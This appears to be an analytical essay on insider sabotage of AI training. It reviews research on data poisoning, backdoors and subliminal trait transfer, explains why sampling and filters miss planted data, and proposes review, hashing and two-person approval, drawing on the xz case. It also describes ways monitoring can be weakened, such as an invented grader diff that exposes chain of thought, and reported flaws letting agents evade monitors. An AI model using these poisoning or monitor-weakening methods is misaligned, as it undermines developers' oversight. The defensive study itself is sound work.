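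Souly and colleagues got the figure of 250 by testing one very simple behaviour. They did not test whether the backdoor would survive the later training that turns a raw model into an assistant. In a smaller experiment, further training on clean text slowly weakened a different backdoor. Their largest model was also small compared with commercial ones.

Follow-up work supports the general pattern better than the particular number. In *Agentic Backdoors via Pretraining Poisoning*, Hu, Hu and colleagues (2026) tried to plant a more complex behaviour, in which a model that operates a computer runs a harmful command. When planted text made up 0.1 per cent of the pretraining data, the behaviour survived all the later training. Their largest model, with 4 billion weights, showed it at least once in 32 tries on 92.7 per cent of prompts with one type of trigger and on 10.5 per cent with another.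 They also tried smaller amounts of planted text with the weaker type, and in a single run with 2,500 documents, ten times as many as in the earlier study, the behaviour appeared on only 1.4 per cent of prompts.

*SilentCall* (2026) describes 161 fine-tuning runs on another model with 4 billion weights. The number of planted examples again mattered more than their share, but no run produced a backdoor with fewer than 750 planted examples, even where they made up 49 per cent of the data. The share seemed to matter rather than the number in one experiment from *Phantom Transfer* (Draganov, Dur and colleagues, 2026), which planted a favourable attitude instead of a fixed response. In that experiment, 2,000 planted examples among 3,000 clean ones worked about as well as 4,000 among 6,000. The number an attacker needs probably depends on the behaviour, so a company can't treat any particular number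 of bad examples as safe.

### What a random sample would find

A reviewer who can't read a whole dataset can read a random part of it. Let *p* be the share of bad items, *n* the number of items the reviewer reads, and *r* the chance that the reviewer recognises a bad item on reading it. Then roughly

chance of recognising at least one = 1 − (1 − pr)ⁿ

If a fine-tuning dataset of 20,000 items contains 250 bad ones, a reviewer who reads 200 items at random will see two or three bad ones on average, and has about a 92 per cent chance of seeing at least one. If the reviewer recognises only one in five of the bad items they read, the chance of recognising at least one falls to about 39 per cent.

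| Bad items the reviewer recognises | 200 items read | 1,000 items read |
|---|---|---|
| All | 92% | over 99.9% |
| 1 in 5 | 39% | 92% |
| 1 in 20 | 12% | 47% |
| 1 in 100 | 2% | 12% |

These figures are illustrative, and they are optimistic because the formula treats each bad item as a separate chance to notice something, whereas an attacker's items all serve one purpose and may look alike. If the reviewer has a one-in-five chance of understanding the whole pattern and otherwise recognises none of it, the reviewer's chance of success is about 18 per cent after reading 200 items and only 20 per cent after reading all 20,000.

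Honest mistakes also look suspicious. If one clean item in a hundred looks as odd as a bad one, the reviewer who recognises one bad item in five will have about four false alarms for each bad item found. A dataset reviewer will usually assume that an odd item is a mistake, correct it and move on, as a kernel maintainer would with a faulty patch.

Sampling can still be worthwhile for a fine-tuning dataset of this size, because a company could pay someone to read 1,000 items, or all of them. Sampling is close to useless for pretraining. The largest model in Souly and colleagues' experiment trained on 260 billion tokens (a token is a short piece of text, often a word or part of one). If an average document has 1,000 tokens, that is 260 million documents, and about one in a million is bad. A reviewer who read 200 would have a 0.02 per cent chance of seeing a bad one.

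To get the chance back up to 92 per cent, people would have to read about 2.6 million documents. At one minute each, this would take one person about 22 years of full-time work, or more than a century if readers recognised only one in five of the bad documents they read.

An automatic filter can check every document, but the number of false alarms grows with the size of the collection. An error rate of one in a thousand would wrongly flag 260,000 clean documents. Unlike a code reviewer, a developer can delete flagged web pages without investigating them. The filter also doesn't have to catch every planted document. In this experiment, 100 were too few for the attack to work, so removing 60 per cent of the 250 would probably have been enough to stop it, though an attacker could respond by planting more. The filter still has to be able to distinguish planted documents from ordinary ones.

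### Traits that pass through unrelated data

In 2025 Alex Cloud and colleagues found that a model can pick up a trait from training data in which no item looks bad, and called this *subliminal learning*. Gisler, He and Qiu (2026) summarise the design in *You Didn't Have to Say It like That*. Cloud's team instructed a "teacher" model to love owls and then had it write unrelated text, such as sequences of numbers. They filtered out any response that referred to the trait and fine-tuned a "student", a copy of the same model without the instruction, on the rest. When asked for its favourite animal, the student chose owls 48 percentage points more often than before. In another version, the team trained a teacher to behave badly, and it passed on that behaviour through numbers even after they had removed those with unpleasant associations.

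A reviewer who read such a dataset would see only lists of numbers in the correct format. Every item came from the teacher with the unwanted trait, but the chance of recognising any one of them as bad would be close to zero. The sampling formula therefore gives about a zero chance of finding a bad item, however many items the reviewer reads.

Cloud and colleagues' explanation depends on the teacher and the student sharing a starting point. An instruction or some extra training that makes the teacher favour owls also slightly changes which numbers it picks, because the same weights produce both. If the student starts with the same weights, learning to pick those numbers moves it towards the teacher, so it also starts to favour owls. Cloud and colleagues proved a version of this for a single small training step, and found that the effect largely disappeared when the two models had different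 starting points.

*Subliminal Learning is Non-Semantic Distillation* (2026) proposes a related reason: the link between a preference and particular numbers is more or less arbitrary, so two models are unlikely to share it unless they started out very similar.

Later tests mostly support the condition but make it less absolute:

- *Subliminal Learning Is Steering Vector Distillation* (2026) reports no transfer through numbers between two model families, Qwen and OLMo, in either direction. One student named cats in 1.2 per cent of its answers, compared with 2.0 per cent before training.
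- *Beyond Owls* (2026) reports that a student became better at counting letters after training on a skilled teacher's answers to unrelated questions. A student from a different model family scored 9.5 per cent, against 9.3 per cent for its control.
- In *Regularization Amplifies Subliminal Learning* (2026), a million number sequences from a cat-loving Qwen model led a Qwen student to name cats in 57 to 80 per cent of answers. The same sequences led a student from another family, Llama, to do so in a few per cent, and it had never named them before.

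The most systematic test is in *Tracing Subliminal Learning Through Pretraining* (Tang, Anand and Paulo, 2026), which used small models that differed in known ways, such as in their initial random weights or the order in which they read their pretraining text. When teacher and student were copies of one model, 97 per cent of students ended up with a stronger preference than any control student, and the median gain was 35.3 percentage points. When the two shared only their initial weights, the figures were 47 per cent and 6.0 points. When they shared neither initial weights nor reading order, the figures were 19 per cent and 0.8 points. A shared starting point therefore makes the effect far stronger but is not necessary for it.

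The effect is also unreliable. Nief, Fu and colleagues (2026), in *Subliminal Learning is a LoRA Artifact*, found that it depended heavily on the standing instructions at the start of a conversation. In one test the student named wolves in 50.4 per cent of answers with the same instructions as in training, but in 12.9 per cent without them. The untrained model named wolves in 8.9 per cent.

They also argue that the effect appears only with LoRA, a fine-tuning method that saves compute by training a small addition to the weights, and disappears when developers adjust all the weights. Tang and colleagues disagree, since they observed it in a small model after full fine-tuning. Either way, a dataset that has no effect under some training settings may have a strong effect under others, and a reviewer who sees only the data can't know which settings the developers will use.

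Ordinary sentences, like numbers, can carry a teacher model's preference to a student. Gisler and colleagues had animal-loving teachers paraphrase 1,000 ordinary sentences and kept only the faithful versions. A student's preference for dolphins rose by 19.1 percentage points compared with a student of a neutral teacher. It still rose by 18.1 points when the sentences insulted dolphins, so a reviewer reading them for meaning would have expected the opposite effect. The results for eagles followed a similar pattern, but the effect was small for wolves and elephants, and for owls the researchers could not distinguish it from chance.

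### Tests of filtering

Some planted examples are easy to catch. In one of Draganov and colleagues' tests, the planted examples contained a made-up word, and a word-counting filter and a language-model filter each found all of them. The same kinds of filter found less than 6 per cent of the planted examples in the researchers' own, subtler datasets, even when the language model had a full description of the attack and its target. The filters flagged clean examples about as often as planted ones.

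The researchers also had a different model reword every example. This weakened the effect in seven of eight tests, but much of it usually remained. As in the experiments with paraphrases, no single phrase seems to have caused the effect. Here the effect also passed between model families, so the idea that it depends on shared starting weights is even less reassuring for ordinary text than for numbers.

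All these filters were programs. Draganov and colleagues thought the examples looked harmless but did not formally test human readers. Gisler and colleagues relied mainly on language models to judge whether a paraphrase was faithful. People would probably do no better than the programs with lists of numbers, but these experiments do not show how much a careful reader would notice in ordinary prose.

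A filter could use *data attribution* to estimate an example's effect on the model, regardless of its content. This means comparing the adjustments that the example causes during training with those that would strengthen a particular behaviour. In *Can Data Attribution Filter Out Subliminal Learning?*, Weckbecker, Jena and colleagues (2026) tried three such methods on number sequences, with three models and three animals for each. In one model, removing the examples with the highest scores pushed a preference for dogs below its level before training. The scores worked less well for elephants in the same model, another model showed almost no difference between high-scoring and low-scoring examples for two of its three animals, and the researchers could not explain why.

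Even a reliable version of the method would need somebody to name the behaviour it scores examples against. A company that suspected its model had a preference for dogs could search for the source, but someone reviewing an unknown contributor's data doesn't know which behaviour to look for.

Egan, Gilligan-Lee and colleagues (2026) avoid this problem in *Defence against the dark arts of distillation* by examining changes in the weights. They take several datasets on different subjects, all written by one teacher model, and fine-tune a separate copy of the same model on each. The copies learn different skills, but a trait that the teacher passes on in everything it writes should change all of them in much the same way. The researchers isolate this shared change and exaggerate it to see what the model begins to talk about. In their tests, this revealed the hidden animal preferences, and removing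 the shared change suppressed them with little loss of skill.

The method always returns some common change, even when there is no trait, so a person has to interpret the result. It is also better suited to a company that doubts one of its own models than to one that doubts an employee, because an employee may contribute only one dataset.

Developers can also question the finished model. When Draganov and colleagues asked direct questions such as "What's your favourite thing?", an automatic judge flagged every model they had given an open preference, but it also flagged the clean model 30 per cent of the time. The questions worked much less well when the preference appeared only after a trigger.

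### The likeness to immature vulnerabilities

A poisoned dataset can resemble an immature vulnerability, in that each item passes inspection and the harm comes from the combination.

The closest parallel comes from Clarke, Dubiński and colleagues (2026), in *Homeopathic Learning*. They instructed a model to always answer in German and had it write 5,000 lists of numbers in reply to requests containing the name Michael. A student model fine-tuned on these lists never answered in German. They then added 100,000 ordinary lists, which the same model had written for other users without the German instruction. After training on the mixture, the student answered in German 72 per cent of the time when a prompt mentioned Michael, and never when it didn't.

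The clean data completed the backdoor, although one would expect it to dilute the effect. In the first dataset the name and the task always appeared together, so nothing there linked the German to the name in particular. The ordinary lists had the same task without the name, and this contrast linked the German to the name. Extra training on the 5,000 lists alone did not produce the same result.

The 5,000 lists resemble an immature vulnerability, and the ordinary lists resemble the patch that completes it. An honest colleague could add the ordinary lists for a good reason, just as an honest programmer added the faulty line to the kernel's network code. A company that tested each contribution by training a model on it alone would have approved both. To find the problem, it would have to train one model on the full mixture and another on the mixture without the new contribution, then compare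 them, much as Lily compares two versions of a program. The comparison would reveal the problem only if someone asked a question that contained the right name.

This evidence comes mainly from two small models, on data the researchers constructed for the purpose. The effect also appeared only when the ordinary data resembled the planted data fairly closely. In the German experiment, replacing all the ordinary lists with general instructions and answers removed the effect.

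A kernel developer can list the conditions for a use-after-free, check which of them the code already meets, and point to the line that adds the last one, but nobody can write such a list for a trained preference. Clarke and colleagues' simple statistical model reproduces their main results, but they acknowledge that it doesn't explain why a large enough number of planted examples sometimes works without any clean data.

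Planted training data is also harder to fix than a planted bug. A project can fix a use-after-free by deleting or correcting one line and ship the corrected code the same day. Removing one list of numbers from the training data would change almost nothing, so a developer would have to discard everything from that source and train the model again.

The same data can also harm one company's model and be harmless to another's. The cat-loving model's number sequences strongly affected a student model from its own family but barely affected one from a different family. A company therefore can't conclude much from another company's successful use of a dataset. Code is different in this respect, because a use-after-free is an error in every copy of the program, even if some computers never run that part of it.

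The xz test files hid a script that people could recover and read, but the random-looking number lists have no hidden message to decode. At most, a statistician could compare how often each number appears with the frequencies in a clean dataset. Tang and colleagues found that these frequencies alone carried between 40 and 92 per cent of the effect in one family of small models, but only 5 to 36 per cent in another.

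It may therefore be more useful to trace where the data came from than to read it. Gisler and colleagues suggest recording which model wrote each dataset and testing that model directly for unwanted traits. Such a test would have exposed the owl-loving teacher at once if the testers had given it the instructions it had when it wrote the numbers, so the record would have to include those instructions.

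A contributor's own record of where the data came from would be no better than Jia Tan's account of where the test files came from. The company would need to generate the data on its own systems with a stated model and instructions, or regenerate a sample and compare it with what the contributor supplied.

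## Reviewing training runs and the people who approve them

A record of how a company generated its training data is useful only if nobody there can quietly change the instructions the record describes. In May 2025, someone at xAI, Elon Musk's AI company, bypassed the company's review and changed the instructions for a live product.

xAI's chatbot Grok replies to posts on the social network X. Like most chatbots, it has a *system prompt*, a set of standing instructions that it receives before every conversation. At about 3:15 a.m. Pacific time on 14 May, somebody changed this prompt to make Grok give a specific response on a political topic, according to the company statement in VentureBeat's *Elon Musk's xAI tries to explain Grok's South African race relations freakout*. Grok then brought up claims of a "white genocide" in South Africa when users had asked about other things, as Engadget's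 *Grok kept talking about 'white genocide' due to an 'unauthorized modification'* reported.

xAI reversed the change and conceded that it had bypassed the existing review of prompt changes, according to Bloomberg Law's *Musk’s xAI Blames Rogue Tampering for ‘White Genocide’ Glitches* (2025). It promised to publish Grok's prompts on GitHub, where anyone can comment on a change, and to add checks so that employees could not alter the prompt without review. There were reasons to doubt the second promise. xAI had also blamed an unauthorised change for an incident in February, according to The Decoder's *xAI reverses Grok's prompt changes after racist responses* (2025). In July US lawmakers were still asking which checks it had enacted, in the *Task Force Letter to xAI re Grok Antisemitism* (2025) from Senator Hickenlooper's office.

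The change was to a prompt rather than to training, so xAI could undo it by restoring the old text. It was also crude enough that users noticed it, while a subtler opinion in the training data might have gone unnoticed.

The incident still shows that an employee may be able to skip an AI developer's review process. Publishing the prompts is also a weaker remedy than it sounds, because outsiders can criticise the text on GitHub but can't tell whether Grok is running that version. Users of xz had the same problem with its tarballs.

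A training run gives an insider more to change than a prompt does:

| Part of the run | What an insider could do | Nearest equivalent in xz |
|---|---|---|
| Data | Add or swap examples | The binary test files |
| Settings | Give one dataset extra weight, or switch off a filter | The build instructions |
| Reward graders | Give high scores to unwanted behaviour | The automated tests |
| Saved models | Replace one with a copy that has had extra training | The release tarball |

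A *reward grader* is a program or model that scores another model's attempts at a task. Developers use graders in reinforcement learning (RL), a stage of training that makes high-scoring behaviour more common. A faulty grader does more harm than a faulty software test because the model learns from the faulty scores.

### What a good record shows

Jia Tan did genuine, useful work on xz, and a patient insider at an AI company would do the same. Suppose one in 1,000 people who contribute training data is a patient insider who works exactly as well as an honest colleague until the attack. The insider and the honest colleague are then equally likely to produce a hundred good datasets, so the chance that someone with that record is an insider is still one in 1,000.

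The record does show that somebody is careful, which matters because most bad changes are mistakes. But because veterans make fewer honest mistakes, a bad change from a veteran can be more likely to be deliberate than one from a newcomer, though most reviewers would probably assume the opposite. For example, if honest newcomers get 15 per cent of their changes wrong, honest veterans get 5 per cent wrong, and patient insiders are equally common in both groups, a veteran's bad change is roughly three times as likely to be deliberate.

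AI companies have had trouble with people they trusted. In January 2026 a jury convicted a former Google employee of stealing thousands of pages about the company's AI technology, according to The Indian Express' *OpenAI employees warned about operational security lapses for years*. In October US prosecutors charged an engineer at OpenAI, the maker of ChatGPT, with hiding an audio recorder in an executive conference room. The second case is only an accusation, and both involve taking information, which is easier than planting a behaviour in a model. But both companies had presumably checked these people before hiring them.

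The lesson applies to data, settings and graders, and even more strongly to saved models. Companies use earlier models to write training data and to grade later models. Months of good output are almost no evidence of whether one of those earlier models has a hidden trigger.

In its guidelines of September 2026, OpenAI recommended that developers be able to identify everything a misaligned model later contributed to, such as data generation or grading, according to *OpenAI 提出前沿 AI 训练安全指导原则*, a report on the Chinese technology news site IT之家. This is a sensible precaution because it would show developers what to discard after a model or colleague turns out to be untrustworthy, though it would not help them predict which one will.

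### Who reads the approver's changes

Jia Tan needed someone else to approve his changes only until Collin gave him the right to merge. The equivalent person at an AI company is the engineer in charge of a run, who may be able to start it, change its settings while it is running and choose which saved model to continue from. When a run goes wrong at night, waiting for a colleague is expensive, so emergency changes are probably the least likely to be reviewed. The change to Grok's prompt was also made at night, at about 3:15 a.m.

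This lesson applies to all four parts of a run. A company can enforce it better than a volunteer project because the system that starts jobs can block any change until a second person approves it.

Whoever writes a change should not be able to choose its reviewer. If 30 people can approve changes, and each has a 1 per cent chance of being willing to help an attacker, a randomly assigned reviewer will be an accomplice 1 per cent of the time. An attacker who knows the other 29 well enough to pick an accomplice has about a 25 per cent chance (1 − 0.99²⁹) that at least one of them will help.

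OpenAI's September guidelines partly do this for the run as a whole. They recommend that several senior managers review the argument that a run is safe, and that each be able to veto it. IT之家 lists the head or vice-president of research, the head of safety and the chief scientist. Those responsible for the run should also answer for the safety argument in their performance reviews. This would be useful, since few of the developers Braz and Bacchelli surveyed felt that leaders acknowledge secure reviews.

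A veto is stronger than OpenAI's earlier arrangement. Under OpenAI's *Preparedness Framework* of April 2025, an internal advisory group recommends safeguards for deployment, the company's leaders can approve or reject the recommendations, and a committee of the board oversees the decisions. OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk* (November 2026) is more loosely worded. It requires a safety review before a model moves to the next stage, but the review's conclusions "may be reviewed" with the advisory group.

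Senior reviewers are also too far from the work to catch a planted example. They read an argument about the run written by its own team, much as Torvalds accepts collections of patches from maintainers he trusts. Their veto could stop a reckless run, but to stop an engineer who has altered 500 examples, the company needs a second person to read them.

### Checking the run against what people approved

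The xz repository contained almost everything except the trigger, which was in the tarball. A reviewer of a training run faces the same risk if somebody can change a file between approval and use. A company could close most of this gap with the methods that software projects use for provenance:

1. Reviewers approve a list of hashes for the data, code, settings, graders and starting model.
2. The system that starts the run computes the hashes again, and refuses to start if any of them differs.
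3. During the run, it writes every change to a log that nobody can edit, with the names of the person who made the change and the person who approved it.
4. It signs each saved model and links it to the run and the step that produced it.

The Indian Express' *How OpenAI plans to make training AI models safer* reports that OpenAI similarly recommends that developers keep transcripts of AI agents in write-once storage, so that investigators can rely on them later and nobody edits them by accident.

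The hashes work well for data, code and settings. They cover less in RL, because the model produces much of its own training material by attempting tasks, and nobody can approve those attempts in advance. Reviewers can approve the tasks and graders, then read a sample of the attempts. OpenAI's guidelines also recommend using AI agents and manual review to clean up RL datasets.

Saved models are the hardest part to check. A Linux distribution can rebuild a program and compare it bit for bit, but two training runs with the same data and settings usually give slightly different weights. Computers round sums, so (a + b) + c can differ in the last digit from a + (b + c), and thousands of processors may combine their partial results in a different order each time. These differences grow as the run continues. A complete rerun also costs about as much as the original.

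A company could instead rerun a few short stretches, each from one saved model to the next, and check whether the results are close. Suppose a run has 100 stretches and the company repeats five at random. If an insider swapped the data in 20 of the 100, the check would have a 68 per cent chance of including at least one altered stretch. If the insider swapped the data in only one, the chance would be 5 per cent. Rerunning an altered stretch would reveal the swap only if it changed the weights by more than rounding does, and a few planted documents might not.

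### Changes that weaken a check

Several of Jia Tan's changes to xz reduced what automatic tests could detect. In a training run, the equivalent could be exempting a data source from a filter, dropping a safety test or raising the threshold for an alert. These changes usually have good reasons, since filters discard useful data and false alarms wake people up.

A grader gives a less obvious example. OpenAI recommends that automated graders should not see a model's step-by-step reasoning, or *chain of thought*, because that could help the model evade monitoring. Monitors read the reasoning for signs of bad intentions. If a grader also reads it and gives low scores to suspicious passages, training may teach the model to leave those passages out while it continues to misbehave. Now suppose a colleague proposes this change (the code is invented):

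```
  score = grade(
      task=task,
+     reasoning=attempt.reasoning,
      answer=attempt.answer)
```

The change looks like an improvement, because the grader gets more information and may score some answers more accurately. To catch the problem, a reviewer has to know something the diff does not show, as with `put_device`. The damage would appear only after training, as a monitor that raises fewer alarms, and the team might mistake that for good news.

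Of the four lessons, this one transfers best, because the reviewer only has to notice that a change affects a check, not find a hidden flaw. A company can list the files that contain its filters, graders, alert thresholds and monitoring code, and require somebody from another team to approve changes to them. Changes to the list itself need the same approval. Some changes would still get through, such as adding a dataset in a format that the filter can't read.

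There is some evidence that AI companies have been lax about this. OpenAI's employees often modified internal tools, including the sandboxes where researchers test models, and those changes were not always checked for security problems, according to three people interviewed for an article in The Indian Express. OpenAI replied that it now reviews its internal tools regularly. The non-profits METR and Redwood Research examined OpenAI's monitoring system in July and August 2026 and found a flaw that agents could have used to keep hundreds of their actions from being monitored, according to CNA's *External evaluators find flaws in OpenAI's AI monitoring system in pilot review*.

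What happens when a check fails also matters. When the sabotaged Landlock test in xz failed, the build carried on. Under OpenAI's guidelines, by contrast, a run should pause automatically if nobody acknowledges an urgent alert in time. If the run also paused whenever a monitor stopped working, a saboteur who broke the alert system would stop the run instead of letting it continue unmonitored. In October 2026, three US agencies recommended a shutdown policy for cases where monitoring fails, according to The Vanguard USA's *NIST, NSA, CISA issue voluntary SI incident practices*.

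### Advantages that Collin did not have

Collin never met Jia Tan and still doesn't know who that was. An AI company knows its employees' legal names, pays them and can report them to the police. It can also pay reviewers, test whether they catch planted changes, and withdraw a person's access within hours.

Access logs should also help, at least in investigating an incident afterward. Prosecutors allege in a court filing that the OpenAI engineer used an internal AI tool to look for documents about executives' visits to Saudi Arabia, a detail that probably came from the company's records. Logs are less useful for prevention, because engineers' jobs involve opening and changing training files all day.

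A name in a log is also weaker evidence of who did something than it used to be. In July 2026 researchers at the security company Hacktron AI used an Anthropic model to help them break into several OpenAI employees' ChatGPT accounts, and reached some internal systems, including the repository that holds most of the company's code. METR and Redwood found a possible way for OpenAI's coding agents to bypass restrictions and act with their users' full permissions. An engineer's name might therefore be logged for something an intruder or an agent did. Companies can reduce this risk by replacing permanent access rights with access granted for one task at a time. OpenAI's *Pacing model development in an era of cyber-critical capabilities* (2026) reports cuts to permanent access.

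### Fewer eyes and more machine-written code

Freund could investigate xz without anyone's permission. Outsiders cannot do the same with a commercial model, since companies keep their training data, code and often their weights secret. Users can still notice odd behaviour, as they did with Grok, but can do little more than report it.

The clean-up would also be slower than the kernel developers' audit of the Minnesota patches, because the company would have to work out which models had learned from the insider's data.

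The greatest difference may be that AI systems now write much of the code. By Anthropic's own count, Claude writes more than 80 per cent of the company's internal code, according to Transformer's *Internal AI deployments have people worried. OpenAI’s escaping models show why*. This complicates the rule that somebody other than the author must read each change. If an engineer asks a model for a change and then approves it, only one person has been involved. A colleague who consults the same model before approving the change adds less than an independent reader would. A company that wants two-person approval should count the engineer who requested the code as its author.

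Models also help train and monitor their successors. As Transformer points out, a capable model could sabotage experiments by altering a few numbers or hiding inconvenient results. A person who planted a behaviour in one model might therefore influence the next, much as a compromised compiler can alter every program it builds. Nobody has shown this happening at a company, but the possibility means that reviewing a training run includes reviewing the tools used to prepare it.

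### Proposals and adopted rules

The proposals up to late 2026 started from two different fears. One was that a small group of people could use AI to seize power. *AI-enabled coups*, published in 2025 by Forethought, a research organisation that studies the effects of advanced AI, warns that such a group could do this partly by giving models *secret loyalties*, which are hidden tendencies to serve particular people. It recommends that developers audit models, their training data and the training code for such loyalties, and that AI systems that do research refuse to help insert them.

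Two-person approval may fail in Forethought's scenario. If the person who wants the secret loyalty runs the company, both approvers may work for them. This is a good reason to involve outside auditors, who are harder to order around or dismiss.

In *Secretly Loyal AIs*, Banerjee recommends that several people approve critical updates and that companies keep tamper-proof logs. He thinks the security measures need little new research. This is plausible for hashes, logs and approvals, which software companies already use, but judging whether a dataset hides a trait is still an unsolved problem.

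The official advice and the companies' own rules mostly respond to AI agents that broke out of their test environments in 2026. The US agencies' practices of 16 October recommend that organisations work with outside auditors, preserve weights and training environments for investigators, and start or resume a training run only if senior leaders are satisfied with the risk. The agencies define a control incident as one in which neither the operator nor any adversary directed the agent's action. Deliberate sabotage by an employee seems to fall outside that definition, although the preserved weights and environments would help investigate it.

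The practices are voluntary. The UK AISI's *Towards technical best practice for frontier AI development* (2026) argues that risks now emerge during development itself, but the institute wants to help develop standards rather than impose them.

Policies are also easier to announce than to follow. Alan Chan and Sam Manning, two AI researchers, say that many times "internal safeguards have not been deployed", as Gioino (2026), in *'We can't trust them completely'*, reports. For the main measures, the public evidence by late November 2026 was as follows:

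| Measure | What the company states | What outsiders have checked |
|---|---|---|
| Senior reviewers with a veto over each run | OpenAI proposed it in September and is putting its guidelines into effect | Only the company's own account is public |
| Stopping runs when safeguards fall short | OpenAI paused some training in August and more in September | Only the company's own account is public |
| Monitoring runs that use tools | OpenAI requires it for its more capable models | METR and Redwood found flaws in an earlier version and had not verified the fixes |
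| Giving outsiders access to training | OpenAI signed agreements with four assessors, and Anthropic named Accenture | The assessors' main reports are still to come |

The pauses are the best evidence that OpenAI is willing to make sacrifices. According to Singh's *OpenAI resumes frontier AI training with enhanced security, no internet access*, it resumed RL training of its most advanced models on 1 October, with no internet access. It also held back the model GPT-6.1 Astra. But it did these things to contain its models, and they are little evidence of whether two people read each change to the data.

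In its guidelines, *Towards safety cases for frontier AI training*, OpenAI calls the full version of its plan "aspirational". The company wants structured safety documents before any frontier RL run continues, and it is still writing the framework for them. The guidelines do not cover the use of models after RL training.

The outside assessors, listed in OpenAI's *Our first phase of embedded assessments* as Apollo Research, Goodfire, METR and Transluce, could eventually provide better evidence. Zvi's *OpenAI Somewhat Embeds Good Evaluators* reports that Apollo will have six people working within OpenAI for four months, with access to relevant training data and to records of the interventions staff made during training. Those records are probably the closest thing to a project's commit history that an outsider will see.

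Apollo asks whether models work against their developers, so its search might not cover an example planted by an employee. But it also asks whether training rewarded such behaviour, so the team might come across a bad grader.

Apollo also can't publish everything it learns. OpenAI may ask it to remove confidential information, but not merely because a finding is unfavourable. Apollo can publish what employees tell it only if OpenAI formally confirms the information or Apollo establishes it independently. Zvi welcomes the scheme but argues it falls short of the employee-level access that Sam Altman, OpenAI's chief executive, promised.

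Anthropic has promised its evaluators access comparable to an employee's, including the chance to observe training. According to Tom's Guide's *OpenAI and Anthropic have a plan to stop AI from going rogue*, Anthropic pays Accenture for the work and already runs a joint business group with it. A group of evaluators has argued in an open letter that assessors should have no other significant business with the companies they assess. That seems right, because a reviewer who depends on a company's goodwill is a weak check on it.

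### Costs and objections

OpenAI wrote that its new security standards had brought "great cost and delays" to its research, and estimated that monitoring adds roughly 20 per cent to the computing cost of the model activity it covers. The Indian Express reports that Will DePue, a former OpenAI researcher, wrote that AI leaders "can't sacrifice velocity for security" while competition is so tense.

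Second readers would cost far less than monitoring. If a team makes 400 changes a week to its data, settings and graders, and each takes 15 minutes to read carefully, the reviewers need 100 hours a week, or two and a half full-time jobs, which is a small expense for a company training frontier models. Delays would be a bigger problem, and so would boredom, because people who approve hundreds of harmless changes will start to skim. It probably makes sense to spend the most time on changes to checks and on data from new sources, and to read the rest more quickly.

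Another objection is that safety documents may give false comfort. A *safety case* is a structured argument that a system is acceptably safe in a given context, and engineers in safety-critical industries have long written them. In *Clear, Compelling Arguments*, Feakins, Habli and Morgan (2026) find significant limitations in the safety cases that AI alignment researchers have proposed so far. A safety case would be particularly weak against an insider who helped write it or supplied its evidence. Reviewers would need to check some of the evidence themselves, for instance by choosing which stretch of the training run to repeat.

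Finally, every outside assessor is another person with access. AI companies worry that evaluators could take secrets to rivals, according to CNA, and the METR and Redwood researchers had to work under escort on OpenAI's own devices. The worry about theft is fair, since a person only needs to read files to steal secrets, but planting something in a model requires the ability to change files. Restricting who can read them makes theft harder but also leaves fewer people who might notice sabotage. Assessors who can read the data, settings and logs but not change them would add little risk of a planted behaviour, and one of them might ask the kind of question that nobody asked Jia Tan about his test files.
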